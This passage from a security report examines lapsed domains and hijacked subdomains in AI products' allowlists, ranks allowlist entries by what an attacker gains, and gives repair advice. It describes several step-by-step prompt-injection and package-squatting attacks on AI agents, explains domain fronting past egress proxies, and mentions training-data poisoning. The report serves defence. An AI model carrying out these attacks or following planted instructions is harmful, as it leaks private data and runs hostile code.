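Five studies give very different numbers, mainly because they counted different things:

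| Study | What the researchers searched | What they counted | Number |
|---|---|---|---|
| Liu and colleagues, 2016 | A million popular domains, plus subdomains of 10,000 popular sites, 2,700 .edu zones and 1,700 .gov zones | Records that they confirmed an attacker could exploit | 791 |
| Borgolte and colleagues, 2018 | 130 million domains pointing to cloud addresses | Domains whose address seemed free | Over 700,000 |
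| *Can I Take Your Subdomain?*, 2020 | 26 million subdomains of 50,000 popular sites | Subdomains pointing to an abandoned service or a lapsed domain | 1,520 |
| Frieß and colleagues, 2024 | 1.5 million cloud-hosted names, growing to 3.1 million over three years | Names that attackers had actually hijacked | 17,698 |
| Lin and colleagues, 2024 | 89 million subdomains, of which 337,284 were on 45 CDNs | Subdomains still pointing to a CDN service that the owner had ended | 1,449 |

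The studies differ most in how they treated cloud addresses that did not respond. Borgolte and colleagues counted a domain if its address failed to respond to regular tests. *Can I Take Your Subdomain?* reports two totals from a single scan: 1,520 subdomains when unresponsive addresses are excluded and 189,017 when they are included, about 124 times as many. The researchers called the additional cases only "potentially vulnerable" because their test could produce false positives. Liu and colleagues similarly separated 5,982 potential cases from their 791 confirmed ones.

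The studies also covered different services. In *Can I Take Your Subdomain?*, 83% of the confirmed cases involved abandoned services, and four companies (WordPress, Shopify, Tumblr and GitHub) accounted for 93% of those. Frieß and colleagues did not monitor WordPress sites, so their data barely overlap with those cases.

Frieß and colleagues found more hijacked names than *Can I Take Your Subdomain?* found vulnerable ones, but the studies used different methods. Frieß and colleagues monitored only names in the cloud and added up three years of hijacks, while the earlier scan tested popular sites' subdomains roughly once. Their paper also gives a separate total of 20,904 hijacks, perhaps because attackers hijacked some names more than once.

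In their summary, Lin and colleagues describe more than 332,000 subdomains as "vulnerable to domain abuse", a much larger figure than the one in the table. Their owners were still using most of these subdomains. The figure includes nearly every subdomain on the 43 CDNs with any of three flaws, and only one of those flaws allows a takeover.

The most common flaw, which 40 of the 45 CDNs had, allows domain fronting. In domain fronting, a program opens an encrypted connection to a trusted host on the CDN but uses it to request a different site on the same CDN. If the CDN doesn't compare the two names, it delivers the request to the other site, which may belong to an attacker.

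Domain fronting doesn't help an attacker get an image past a CSP allowlist, because the browser uses the same name in the TLS handshake and the HTTP Host header. Code running in an agent's sandbox can use a different name in each, and an egress proxy that sees only the TLS name would let the request through. A reviewer of an egress allowlist should therefore take the larger figure seriously, even though it is weak evidence about dangling records.

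*Can I Take Your Subdomain?* also tested what a hijacker could do to sites that trusted related subdomains. The researchers examined the 887 sites with a confirmed vulnerable subdomain, visiting up to six pages on each of up to 200 related hosts. On 20 sites, a CSP allowed a vulnerable subdomain to supply a frame (a web page displayed inside another page). They found no site where a takeover would have given an attacker a new way to inject scripts, mostly because the script policies were already weak. Of the 1,144 hosts with such a policy, 901 had one that any attacker could bypass.

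The researchers did not test image policies this way, so their results don't include an estimate of how many sites would have let a hijacked subdomain collect data through image requests, as Noma's server did in ForcedLeak.

### What hijackers have done with subdomains

Most of the known hijackers wanted search traffic. Frieß and colleagues found that 75% of the hijacked pages they collected used deceptive techniques to rank higher in search results. Many of the pages promoted gambling sites, which paid for the visitors. The hijackers benefited from the reputation of the domains they used. 31% of Fortune 500 companies lost control of at least one subdomain. Many hijacks ended within 15 days, but more than a third lasted longer than 65 days.

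The researchers found almost no malware. They did find 83 stolen login cookies (small files that keep a user signed in) linked to three of the hijacked subdomains. This number is small, but the researchers could detect a theft only if someone leaked or sold the cookies.

The CDC hijacker was part of a similar business. Portal and Burton named the actor Hazy Hawk and traced its hijacks back to at least December 2023. They list about 130 parent domains, including those of Deloitte, UNICEF and the University of California, Berkeley. Hazy Hawk filled the subdomains with links advertised as videos, often pornography or pirated content. The links led through redirects to scams and fake applications. Some pages also asked for permission to send browser notifications, which let the scammers keep contacting visitors.

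One of the subdomains Hazy Hawk hijacked had hosted a French government website for the Olympic Games. The government took the site down after the event but left its DNS record in place. An allowlist with a wildcard for any of the affected domains would have allowed the hijacked subdomain for as long as Hazy Hawk held it.

Hazy Hawk is one of several such operations. Infoblox has also described hijacked aliases that led visitors to fake dating services and malware. But Infoblox's short profile *Hazy Hawk* lists the actor's prevalence as "Uncommon". Portal and Burton explain that abandoned cloud resources are hard to find because each provider responds differently when a resource is missing. They believe Hazy Hawk has access to a commercial database of past DNS traffic and does much of the checking by hand.

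Like EchoLoc, these studies would probably miss an attacker who only collects data from image requests. Frieß and colleagues detected hijacks by looking for changes in web pages, and the CDC case was discovered because pornographic links appeared in search results.

Blocklists would not help much either. Antivirus companies had flagged only 135 of the hijacked names that Frieß and colleagues found. Certificate Transparency logs are more promising, because owners can get an alert when an authority issues a certificate for one of their subdomains. Only 18% of the hijacked names had a valid certificate, so these alerts would have missed most of the search spam. The alerts should work better for names on AI allowlists, since an attacker usually needs a certificate to receive encrypted requests.

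### Whether hijacked subdomains threaten AI agents

Bachu (2026), in *Dangling DNS*, argues that AI agents make subdomain takeover more dangerous. The article appears on the website of Akamai, a CDN and security company, and promotes its product for finding dangling records. It describes a hypothetical attack:

1. An attacker claims the abandoned Azure site behind analytics.mycompany.com.
2. An employee asks an AI agent to summarize a page on that subdomain.
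3. The page contains hidden instructions to look up internal company data.
4. The agent follows them and puts a summary of the data into the attacker's page.
5. The attacker collects the summary.

The CDC case shows that the first step is realistic, and ForcedLeak shows that an agent can follow planted instructions and retrieve private data. Bachu reports no test or incident that combines the two. Frieß and colleagues, and Portal and Burton, describe hijacks that targeted people and search engines, not AI agents.

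The fourth step is the weakest because a web page can't normally read what an assistant writes in its own window. The agent would have to type the summary into a form on the page or request a web address that contains it. Some agents can do this, but Bachu doesn't show that any product would do so without asking the user.

Whether an AI agent trusts a company's subdomains depends on the product and its settings, so Bachu's claim that agents trust them automatically is too general. An attacker doesn't need a takeover just to plant hidden instructions, because an agent may follow them on a page at any domain. A takeover helps most when the product has an allowlist entry such as `*.mycompany.com`, because the attacker can then both supply the instructions and receive the data at a trusted address.

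AI may also help attackers find abandoned resources. *From Forgotten to Exploited*, a CircleID article by an employee of the domain management company CSC, says that AI makes it faster to analyze thousands of subdomains and match them to cloud services. The article gives no data for this, and CSC has a commercial interest in the problem. It is still plausible, because an AI agent could do the repetitive work of reading each provider's error messages and deciding which resources a stranger could claim.

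## Judging what an attacker gains from a trusted domain

The urgency of a bad allowlist entry depends mainly on what the product does with the domain. An allowlist permits requests but doesn't make them. If the product contacts the domain in normal use, for instance to install software, the domain's new holder only has to respond to those requests. If it doesn't, an attacker must first get the product to make a request, usually through prompt injection.

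This ranking starts with the entries where an attacker needs the least help:

| Rank | What the product does with the domain | What the new holder gains | What else must hold for harm |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Installs or runs code from it | Control of whatever that code can reach | The product still requests the code and doesn't check it against a known fingerprint or signature |
| 2 | Sends it secrets or private data in normal use | The contents of each request | The product still makes those requests |
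| 3 | Reads text from it | A place to plant instructions | The agent opens the page, follows the instructions and has the power to do something harmful |
| 4 | Permits requests to it but makes none in normal use | A place to collect stolen data | An injection works somewhere else, the agent can read private data, and no other control stops the request |

The rank reflects how easily an attack could succeed, not how much it would harm the victim. As far as anyone outside Salesforce knows, the domain in ForcedLeak belonged in rank 4, yet the researchers used it to obtain customers' email addresses. Conversely, hostile code in a sandbox with no passwords or private files might do little damage. A reviewer with several entries of the same rank should start with the entry whose product can read the most private data or take the most serious actions.

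An entry with several uses should take the rank of its highest-ranked use. For example, a domain that an agent reads pages from belongs in rank 3, even if an attacker could also use it to collect stolen data.

In a CSP, how an attacker can use a domain depends on the directive that lists it. An `img-src` entry lets the page load images from the domain, so it usually belongs in rank 4. A `script-src` entry belongs in rank 1 if the page loads a script from the domain, because that script could read what the user sees and act in the user's name. If the page loads no such script, the attacker also needs a flaw that lets them insert one.

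The table below applies the ranking to some entries from earlier sections. Only the Salesforce domain is known to have lapsed, so the other rows are hypothetical.

| Entry | What the product does with it | Rank if a stranger controlled it |
|---|---|---|
| `*.my-salesforce-cms.com` in Salesforce's image list | Permitted images, with no known regular use | 4 |
| gems.rubyforge.org in Copilot's preset | May install packages from it for an old Ruby project | 1 for such a project, otherwise 4 |
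| Host for a "network secret" in Claude Code | Adds an API key to requests | 2 |
| pheweb.jp in Claude Science's list | Looks up research data | 3 |
| Script host on a page that uses `'strict-dynamic'` | Modern browsers ignore the entry | None, except in old browsers |

The RubyForge row shows why a reviewer should look at the customer's projects as well as the vendor's list. If a team has no old Ruby code, a stranger who controlled the domain could use it only to collect stolen data, and would need a working injection to do so. A team whose build files still name the old package source could install the stranger's code without any injection. Deleting the allowlist entry might not protect that team. Codex, for example, gives setup scripts full internet access, so an old installer could still contact rubyforge.org during setup after the deletion.

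### Data sent and trust inherited

The new holder of a domain may receive much more than requests from one AI product. According to Infoblox, quoted in The Hacker News' *Hackers Spend Nearly $7 Million on Expired Domains to Redirect Traffic* (2026), an old domain comes with email meant for the previous holder, cached search results and web traffic, among other things. The email could include password-reset messages for accounts the previous holder never closed.

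The closest precedent for abuse of lapsed allowlist entries comes from email. A company can publish a DNS record, called an SPF record, that lists the servers allowed to send email in its name. The record can also import another domain's list with an instruction such as `include:partner.example`. If partner.example lapses, whoever registers it can publish a new list containing their own servers. Receiving mail systems will then treat those servers as authorized by the company.

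In February 2024, the security company Guardio Labs described a spam operation that it named SubdoMailing. The operators registered lapsed domains that were still in companies' sender lists. They also hijacked subdomains, such as marthastewart.msn.com, whose aliases pointed to lapsed domains. Guardio counted more than 8,000 domains and 13,000 subdomains in the operation, which sent millions of messages a day. Those totals cover both methods, so they don't show how many lapsed domains the operators found in sender lists.

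SubdoMailing is good evidence that criminals will search other people's allowlists for lapsed domains when it pays. But the reward is different in an AI product. The spammers could use any well-known brand and made money from volume, while someone who buys a domain on an AI product's allowlist usually still needs a working prompt injection and a victim with valuable data.

Also in 2024, the security company watchTowr paid $20 for dotmobiregistry.net, an expired domain that many programs still trusted. The registry for .mobi names had let it expire after moving its WHOIS server to a new address. WatchTowr started its own WHOIS server on the old domain. Within a week, more than 135,000 systems had sent it about 2.5 million queries, because their software still contained the old address.

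Controlling the answers to WHOIS queries was more dangerous than seeing the queries, which mostly reveal which domain somebody is looking up. Some certificate authorities used WHOIS records to find the email address of a domain's owner, then sent a message there to confirm a certificate request. WatchTowr showed that one of them, GlobalSign, would accept a watchTowr address as the contact for microsoft.mobi. The researchers stopped before obtaining a certificate.

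A reviewer who looked only at the data leaving those systems would have ranked the domain too low. A reviewer could make the same mistake with an AI product that sends a harmless lookup to an allowlisted domain and then relies on the reply.

### Text that an agent reads

For its Web Hole study of October 2026, AIR Security examined roughly 6,500 sites and found 36 unregistered domains in search results, about 0.6% of the sites examined. Besides pyquestions.com, they included thestackoverflow.com, which came up for a question about the programming framework AngularJS.

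Antipov describes how an attack on Anthropic's Claude could work:

1. An attacker registers one of the names and puts instructions for AI agents on the page.
2. Claude searches the web and receives a list of results with short descriptions.
3. Claude opens the page with a separate tool, and a language model summarizes it.
4. The instructions survive in the summary, where they look like reference material.
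5. Claude acts on them.

The fourth and fifth steps are the uncertain ones, because a summary may drop the instructions and the agent may ignore any that remain. The result also depends on what the agent can do. An agent that only reports what it found may give a wrong answer, whereas one with access to a terminal could run the attacker's commands. AIR Security described this only as a possible attack.

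The company also found sites that addressed AI agents directly, sites that showed bots one page and ordinary browsers another, and a GitHub project with malicious commands in its README. None of these requires a lapsed domain. A lapsed domain is most useful to an attacker when the agent is allowed to read only from domains on an allowlist.

Researchers studied a related problem in training data before agents were common. Large image collections often consist of web addresses and captions, and each user downloads the images separately. In 2023, Carlini and colleagues pointed out that anyone who bought a lapsed domain in such a collection could replace its images for everyone who downloaded it afterwards. They calculated that in 2022 an attacker could have controlled 0.01% of the images in LAION-400M or COYO-700M for $60. They bought some of the domains and logged the requests, but didn't serve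 altered images.

Some of the collections' maintainers later began to publish a fingerprint of each image, so that a downloader can reject a file that has changed. But the downloader then also rejects images that a site has resized or recompressed for innocent reasons.

In October 2025, researchers at Anthropic, the UK AI Security Institute and the Alan Turing Institute reported that planting about 250 documents in a language model's training data could give it a hidden flaw, whether the model had 600 million or 13 billion parameters. The flaw was mild and only made the model produce gibberish after a certain phrase. The study didn't use lapsed domains, so it supports only the claim that an attacker may not need to control many pages.

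### Code that a product runs

A lapsed domain is most dangerous when software already runs code from it, since the new holder doesn't have to trick anyone. In 2012, Nikiforakis and colleagues examined scripts that the 10,000 most popular websites loaded from other domains. They found 56 domains that anyone could register, used by 47 of the sites. They bought two. In 15 days, one of them, blogtools.us, received about 80,000 visits from pages still requesting its script. A hostile owner could have run code in each of those visitors' browsers.

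The researchers also registered a misspelled domain, googlesyndicatio.com, which lacks the final "n" of a Google advertising domain. In the same length of time, the browsers of about 163,000 visitors requested scripts from it. A mistyped domain can therefore be as dangerous as a lapsed one if a page loads something from it.

In February 2025, watchTowr reported a similar test with abandoned storage buckets, the named containers in which Amazon's customers keep files. The company registered about 150 abandoned bucket names for a little over $400 in total. Over about two months, the buckets received more than 8 million requests, including some for software updates, programs and server images. Some of the requests came from government and military networks.

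WatchTowr didn't send back hostile files, so the number of requests doesn't show how many machines would have run one. An updater that checks signatures before installing files, for example, could have rejected it. Still, each request gave whoever held the bucket a chance to send a hostile file. Amazon later blocked anyone from claiming the bucket names again.

Amazon storage buckets have addresses under amazonaws.com, so the `*.amazonaws.com` entry in Claude Code's preset would let an agent download a file from an abandoned bucket that a stranger had claimed. For shared storage, a reviewer has to check which bucket the product or project uses and who controls it now.

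Criminals have also taken over traffic from other criminals' attacks. Infoblox's *Dropcatch Scavengers* (2026) describes criminals who buy expired domains that earlier attackers had used. Websites compromised by those attackers still send visitors to the domains, so the buyers can redirect these visitors to scams and malware without breaking into the websites themselves.

Wyss, Davidson and De Carli (2024) analyzed the web addresses in more than two million packages on npm, the main source of JavaScript packages, and concluded that most posed limited security risks. However, broken links and expired domains were more common in less popular packages, so an agent that chooses obscure packages without asking the user is more likely to encounter them.

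### Dead names in instructions for agents

Many websites now publish an llms.txt file, an informal convention for describing a site to AI agents. The file often includes commands for installing the company's software. If a command names a package or domain that nobody has registered, an attacker can register it and wait for an agent to run the command.

Tom's Hardware's *Researchers easily trick Fortune-500 companies' AI agents into running arbitrary code* reports on a study of these files by the security company Pandex, published in August 2026. The unclaimed names included packages in six registries, expired .dev and .io domains, and abandoned subdomains at hosting services such as Vercel and Netlify. 三村 (2026), in *AIエージェント向け「llms.txt」にサプライチェーンリスク*, credits the work to the researcher Alon Hertz. Together with TechRadar's *Top AI tools including Claude, Codex, and Hermes installed suspicious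 code*, these reports give the following figures:

| What Hertz counted | Number |
|---|---|
| Companies in the survey | About 15,000 |
| Live domains with the files | 6,214 |
| Files collected | 8,565 (TechRadar gives 8,265) |
| Domains with at least one unclaimed name | 120 |
| Unclaimed names | At least 237 |

About 1.9% of the live domains therefore had the problem. The 237 names include packages, domains and subdomains, so they are not a count of lapsed domains.

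Hertz then registered some of the package names and uploaded harmless packages that reported back when somebody installed them. The first report arrived after four minutes, from a network he identified as a Fortune 500 company's. A report from a second such company followed within an hour, and TechRadar mentions a few dozen more after that. According to 三村, Hertz did not break into the networks or take data, and he withheld the companies' names because they were still fixing the problem.

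This is the strongest evidence that agents will run code from a name nobody had claimed. Hertz also tested five configurations of leading models with two command-line agents. In some cases, an agent given only a vendor's name found the official instructions itself and installed the unregistered package. The researchers said the tools that installed their code included Claude, Codex and Hermes (an agent from Nous Research).

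The reports from company networks are harder to interpret than the controlled tests. Automated security scanners also install new packages, sometimes within minutes, so an early report could have come from a scanner rather than an agent following instructions. Outsiders who don't know which companies were involved can't check how Hertz distinguished scanners from agents.

An egress allowlist would not reliably have stopped the installation. Agents normally need access to package registries such as pypi.org, and a hostile package comes from the same trusted host as a good one. A strict list could have prevented the package from reporting back to the researchers, but the code would already have run in the sandbox. The number of reports may therefore understate the number of installations.

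Hertz also found that a third party had already registered one of these names. Clerk, which provides login services, included a command from its own software in its instructions for agents. As written, the command could make npx, a tool for running npm packages, look for a public package with the same name as the command. The third party had uploaded a package under that name, with code that sent information about the user's machine to an outside server. Clerk has since corrected its instructions to specify its own package, `@clerk/eslint-plugin`.

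Hertz classed the package as malicious. The package shows that outsiders were already claiming such names, but not how many machines installed it or whether an AI agent was responsible for any installation.

Placeholder domains create a similar problem. Many programmers use third-party.com as a made-up address in examples, just as they would use example.com. But example.com is permanently reserved for this purpose, whereas anyone could register third-party.com. Unit 42's *Phantom Squatting* examined another source of unregistered names, the domains that language models invent.

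The Hacker News' *Placeholder third-party[.]com Referenced Across 1,700+ Repositories Now Serves Malicious Content* (2026) reports that Manifold Security found third-party.com serving malicious content to visitors. More than 1,700 public GitHub repositories refer to the domain, some of them with instructions for AI agents. Since at least June 2026, Windows users who opened the site have seen a fake security check. The page copies a command to their clipboard and shows instructions to paste it into a Windows dialog box. The command then downloads and runs more code. Mac users see only a message that the site requires Windows.

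Two days later, *Placeholder Domains Used by 349 AI Agent Skills Found Redirecting to Scams* (Ahmed, 2026) reported a wider finding by the same company. Several placeholder domains appeared in 359,000 GitHub files and 349 agent skills, which are sets of instructions an agent loads for a particular kind of task. Those domains sent some Mac users to scams but hid this from other visitors.

These numbers are counts of references, not of visits by agents. An agent that understands an example will normally replace the placeholder with a real address. The attack on third-party.com also depends on a person pasting a command, although the domain's holder could easily replace the page with instructions for agents. The finding is strong evidence that somebody was abusing the domain, but much weaker evidence that AI agents were among the victims.

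Because these sites hide their behavior, someone who opens third-party.com on a Mac might conclude that it is merely broken. A page that looks harmless therefore shouldn't lower any entry's rank. Registration records are a better guide to whether the expected owner still controls the domain.

### Which cases involved an allowlist

Most of these incidents involve software that encountered an abandoned name, with no allowlist vouching for it:

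| Case | Where the name was | Was that an allowlist? | Who claimed it |
|---|---|---|---|
| ForcedLeak, 2025 | CSP header of an AI product | Yes | Researchers |
| SubdoMailing, 2024 | Lists of permitted email senders | Yes | Criminals |
| .mobi WHOIS server, 2024 | Settings in old software | No | Researchers |
| Training images, 2023 | Lists of files to download | No | Researchers |
| Website scripts, 2012 | Code of web pages | No | Researchers |
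| Storage buckets, 2025 | Update tools and installation instructions | No | Researchers |
| Web Hole, 2026 | Search results | No | Nobody at the time of the check |
| llms.txt, 2026 | Instructions for agents | No | Researchers and, in Clerk's case, an unknown party |
| Placeholder domains, 2026 | Examples in code and agent skills | No | Scammers |

In the Web Hole scenario, a strict allowlist would protect the agent if it also applied to the search and reading tools, because an abandoned site in the results would normally not be on it. In ForcedLeak, the allowlist itself let the request through. Counting Web Hole's 36 domains or the 237 names from llms.txt files as bad allowlist entries would therefore greatly exaggerate the evidence.

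A blocked domain can become an allowlisted one. Suppose a company's installation instructions refer to a lapsed domain that a stranger now owns, and an agent's sandbox blocks it. An administrator who sees the error may add the domain to the allowlist to make the installation work. The administrator would then have given the stranger's domain rank 1 because they trusted the company's own instructions.

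### Whether criminals have used a lapsed entry in an AI allowlist

None of the companies and researchers behind these cases describes a criminal attack through an expired domain on an AI product's allowlist. The closest case is ForcedLeak, in which researchers bought the domain. But Guardio, Pandex, AIR Security and Manifold Security were all investigating something else, so the fact that they reported no such attack is only weak evidence that none has happened.

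An attack of this kind would also be easy to miss, because the victim's logs would show only requests to an approved domain.

Such attacks may also really be rare. Many agents can contact any website, so an attacker can use their own domain. Even a restricted product may allow shared storage that the attacker can rent, as Salesforce's old header apparently did. A lapsed entry is most useful when the rest of the product's allowlist is strict, and the attacker must find it before the vendor or another buyer does.

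A change of ownership does not prove that a listed domain is being used for an attack. *Used domain names are valuable*, from SIDN, the registry for Dutch .nl domains, explains that people who re-register expired names usually have an honest motive, such as using the name for a similar business. But an honest buyer could still sell the domain later, or someone could hack its server. The allowlist entry is wrong even if the new owner has done nothing suspicious, because the vendor approved the previous owner.

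## Repairing a bad entry and keeping the list accurate

There are four ways to repair a bad allowlist entry. A lapsed domain usually needs the first two together.

| Repair | Main advantage | Main weakness | When it fits |
|---|---|---|---|
| Register the domain again | Protects every copy of the list, including copies nobody knows about | Somebody has to keep paying, and it's impossible once a stranger holds the name | The domain has lapsed or is about to |
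| Delete the entry | Costs almost nothing and works even if a stranger holds the name | Changes only the copy that somebody edits | Nothing needs the domain any more |
| Narrow a wildcard to exact hosts | Ends trust in forgotten subdomains | May break the product when the service adds a host | The expected owner still holds the domain |
| Move to a domain the vendor controls | The vendor decides about renewal and DNS | The old name survives in scripts and other lists | The product still needs the content |

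Narrowing a wildcard helps with dangling subdomains and shared cloud domains, but not lapsed domains. For shared domains, PromptArmor advises customers to list the one Azure host they need instead of `*.azure.com`.

Vendors give conflicting advice about wildcards. CodeRabbit recommends exact names because a wildcard would allow more CodeRabbit subdomains than the tool needs. Augment Code, which makes an AI coding assistant, recommends a wildcard so that new subdomains work without further changes. A wildcard saves support work, but the customer bears the added risk. In Copilot's custom list, a plain domain covers all its subdomains, but an administrator can instead enter a full address such as `https://packages.example.com/`. According to GitHub, the firewall then allows only that scheme and host, and only paths under the one given.

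### Secure the name before removing it

The safest order is to secure the name, remove the entry and then search the logs. When a vendor removes an entry from a public list, anyone who compares versions can see which name the vendor has stopped trusting. If that name is for sale, an attacker could buy it while older copies of the list are still in use.

If the domain is in its redemption period, the old holder can still recover it. PyPI's *Preventing Domain Resurrection Attacks* (2025) puts the usual recovery fee at $70 to more than $200. If the domain is open for anyone to register, the vendor should register it the same day. For a dangling record, the domain's owner should delete the record or reclaim the resource behind it.

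If a stranger already holds the name, the vendor should delete the entry at once. It can then try to buy the name back or, if it owns a matching trademark, file a complaint under ICANN's dispute policy.

A company that recovers a retired domain doesn't have to run a server on it. If the domain has no address records, requests to it fail. A server that logs requests would show which clients still use the domain, but it would also collect whatever those clients send, possibly including passwords.

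**The bad entry should be removed.** Removing it can expose uses that nobody recorded. For example, when Copilot's firewall blocks a request, Copilot adds a warning to the pull request with the blocked address and the command that tried to reach it. The right response is to fix that command, not to restore the entry.

The repair should include a **log search** going back to the last date when the expected owner certainly held the domain. The search can wait, but someone should save a copy of the logs as soon as the problem is discovered, because many systems delete old logs automatically.

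The proxy in GitHub's agent firewall logs allowed requests as well as blocked ones, according to a copy of the firewall's guide on skills.sh, a directory of instructions for AI agents. The log therefore includes requests to a bad entry, since the firewall allows them. For encrypted traffic, the log normally contains the host but not the full address, so it can show that an agent contacted the domain but not what the agent sent.

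A log search that finds nothing doesn't prove that nothing happened. Copilot's firewall covers only processes that the agent starts through its command-line tool. In Claude Science, software installations from a company's internal mirror bypass the outbound proxy, and Anthropic warns that they won't appear in the proxy's logs.

If the search finds requests to the domain, the company should replace any key the product sent there and rebuild any environment where the product installed software from it, because deleting the entry doesn't remove code already on the machine. Claude Code, for instance, saves a snapshot after its setup script runs and reuses it for about a week. Changing the allowed hosts triggers a new snapshot, but an existing session can keep its old files.

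### Why deleting the entry may not be enough

An allowlist entry often has copies, sometimes in the same product, and deleting one leaves the others working. Copilot combines an organization's entries with those of each repository, so an entry deleted at one level may remain at the other. In Claude Code, a host attached to a network secret stays reachable until someone deletes the secret. Archiving the environment doesn't remove the secret from sessions already running.

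Caching can also delay a deletion. A browser applies the CSP that arrived with the page, so if an employee leaves a chat window open for days, it keeps the old policy until it reloads. Egress lists can change faster, and existing Claude Code sessions apply a new setting within about a minute.

A bad entry can remain in customers' copies of an allowlist after the vendor removes it from the original. Cursor, a code editor with an AI agent, lets administrators set a company-wide allowlist, but that list replaces the built-in defaults. When a customer asked how to keep the defaults, a Cursor employee replied that the customer would have to add them manually. If Cursor later removes a bad domain from its defaults, the customer's copy won't change.

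Several products have the same problem when a customer wants to cancel just one entry in the vendor's preset:

| Product | How a customer can cancel one preset entry | Does the customer need a copy of the rest? |
|---|---|---|
| GitHub Agentic Workflows | Add the domain to the `blocked` list | No |
| Claude Science | Switch off the domain in the organization's settings, where Anthropic permits it | No |
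| Copilot cloud agent | Turn off the recommended list and write a custom one | Yes |
| Claude Code cloud sessions | Turn off the default list and write a custom one | Yes |
| Codex cloud tasks | Start from the empty list | Yes |
| Cursor | Set a company allowlist | Yes |

A block rule is the better design because the customer still receives the vendor's other corrections. GitHub Agentic Workflows, for example, removes blocked domains and their subdomains from the allowed ones. Customers of the last four products, who must cancel an entry without a block rule, then have to maintain dozens or hundreds of others themselves.

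Other vendors' lists need separate corrections too, as with jcenter.bintray.com, the retired name in the presets of OpenAI, GitHub, Anthropic and Kiro.

Finally, old software keeps connecting to old domain names. The Tor Project's *Deprecation of Azure CDN from Edgio (azureedge.net)* (2024) includes a December 2024 message about a host for Snowflake, a tool for bypassing internet censorship. The writer thought the team hadn't used the host since 2021, but it was still generating monthly bills because somebody was sending it traffic. Editing an allowlist doesn't affect clients like these, so the only protection is to keep control of the domain name.

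### How Microsoft retired its azureedge.net hosts

The host in Tor's message was under azureedge.net, a domain that Microsoft's Azure customers used for content delivery. Edgio, one of the companies whose servers delivered that content, went bankrupt in 2024. The bankruptcy forced Microsoft to move its own software downloads within a few weeks. Microsoft's handling of the old names is a useful model for retiring a trusted domain.

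The team behind .NET, Microsoft's programming platform, announced the move on December 26 in Microsoft's *Critical* (2024). Installers and automated build systems all over the world were downloading .NET from two hosts that the team expected to retire within months:

| Old host | Replacement | What it delivers |
|---|---|---|
| dotnetcli.azureedge.net | builds.dotnet.microsoft.com | Official releases |
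| dotnetbuilds.azureedge.net | ci.dot.net | Builds from ongoing development |

Both replacements are under domains that Microsoft uses for its own products, so the names no longer depend on a delivery supplier. The paths stayed the same, so customers had to change only the host name. Microsoft asked them to search their source code, installation scripts and container files for azureedge.net, and to check that their firewalls allowed the new hosts.

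The announcement also promised that "No other party will ever have access to use these domains." Microsoft didn't explain how it would keep this promise, which appears above a list of only the two .NET hosts. The Hacker News' *NET Domains* (2025) adds that Microsoft had taken control of azureedge.net to stop an attacker from acquiring it and distributing malware.

The retirement then took place in stages:

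| Date | Event |
|---|---|
| December 13, 2024 | Azure stops accepting new Edgio configurations |
| January 15, 2025 | Edgio's platform shuts down, almost ten months earlier than first planned |
| January 23, 2025 | The .NET team reports that trial shutdowns of the old hosts are starting |
| May 31, 2025 | Latest date by which the team expects those hosts to stop working |
| June 11, 2025 | An old host for Azure DevOps, Microsoft's service for building software, is inactive |
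| September 30, 2027 | Support ends for azureedge.net names that customers kept when moving to Azure Front Door, Microsoft's own delivery service |

The trial shutdowns, which Microsoft calls "scream tests", are an easy way to find forgotten uses. The team turns a host off for a while, waits for complaints, and can turn it back on if something important breaks. An allowlist's maintainer can do the same by suspending an entry before deleting it.

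Even with this preparation, references to the old domain survived. hugovk's *azureedge.net CDN will cease operations by 15th January 2025* (2025) reported the domain to the maintainers of Selenium, a browser-testing tool, after a search of the 8,000 most popular Python projects. Within Microsoft, sebastienros's *Update remnants of azureedge.net* (2025) was still replacing references in February. Months later, Valeriamejia1's *Edge driver download fails due to outdated CDN (msedgedriver.azureedge.net)* reported that a published Python library was still requesting another retired host and failing.

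At least one AI allowlist also kept the domain. In August 2026, GitHub's recommended list for Copilot still included four hosts under azureedge.net:

- dotnetcli.azureedge.net, one of the two that the .NET team had retired
- playwright.azureedge.net
- playwright-akamai.azureedge.net
- playwright-verizon.azureedge.net

The last three delivered browsers for Playwright, Microsoft's browser-testing tool. According to a comment in Playwright's *chore: update CDN endpoints*, the "akamai" and "verizon" hosts both ran on Edgio. GitHub's list already contained the replacements for .NET and Playwright, so somebody had added the new names without deleting the old ones. Microsoft owns GitHub, and 20 months had passed since it told the public to search for the domain.

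In April 2026, a list of GitHub-related addresses that Palo Alto Networks publishes for firewalls included the wildcard `*.azureedge.net`. That entry covers GitHub's four hosts and every name that other Azure customers have kept there. The presets for Codex, Kiro and Claude Code don't include azureedge.net.

This doesn't show that the Copilot entries are dangerous today. A stranger could take over one of the four host names only if Microsoft lost azureedge.net or let another customer reuse the name. The entries are just clutter while Microsoft keeps its promise, but a lapse would be serious because Copilot's users could install software from those hosts.

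Microsoft's instructions also helped keep an old entry in place. *CDN Domain URL change for Agents in Pipelines* (2025) told Azure DevOps customers to add the new host to their firewalls and keep vstsagentpackage.azureedge.net until further notice. Keeping the old host was sensible during the move because it prevented failed downloads. But the post still tells customers not to remove that host, even though it now describes it as inactive. A removal date in the original instructions would have avoided this.

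GitHub's list also includes dotnetcli.blob.core.windows.net, a storage address for .NET downloads that is already being retired. Microsoft planned to end anonymous public access to that storage account around July 2026. Closing an account to the public is safer than deleting it, because deletion might let another customer claim the name.

### Holding a retired name is cheaper than finding every copy

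A .com domain typically costs between $10 and $20 a year to renew. At $15 a year, holding a retired name for 20 years costs $300, the same as three hours of searching by an engineer whose time costs $100 an hour. Several teams spent months on the azureedge.net clean-up and still didn't find every copy.

Renewing domains costs little, even for a long list. Salesforce's image allowlist had 15 domains that appeared to belong to Salesforce or Slack and that a stranger could have bought if their registrations lapsed. Renewing all of them at $15 each would cost about $225 a year. Buying a domain back can cost far more. The previously used domains that Infoblox priced sold for about $2,700 each on average.

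A company should therefore keep renewing any domain that it has ever put on an allowlist or in installation instructions, because it may miss some copies of the entry. It should still delete the entries it can find, to protect customers if it no longer holds the domain, perhaps because it has closed or sold the name.

This calculation applies only to the domain's owner. OpenAI can't renew rubyforge.org while somebody else holds it, and buying every third-party name that lapses would make OpenAI responsible for traffic it never wanted. When another company retires a domain, deleting the entry is usually better.

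### Certificates that outlast a change of ownership

After the owner regains a domain, the previous holder may still be able to impersonate the website. Its certificate remains valid until it expires or the issuing authority revokes it, so a previous holder who kept the private key could run a server that browsers accept as genuine.

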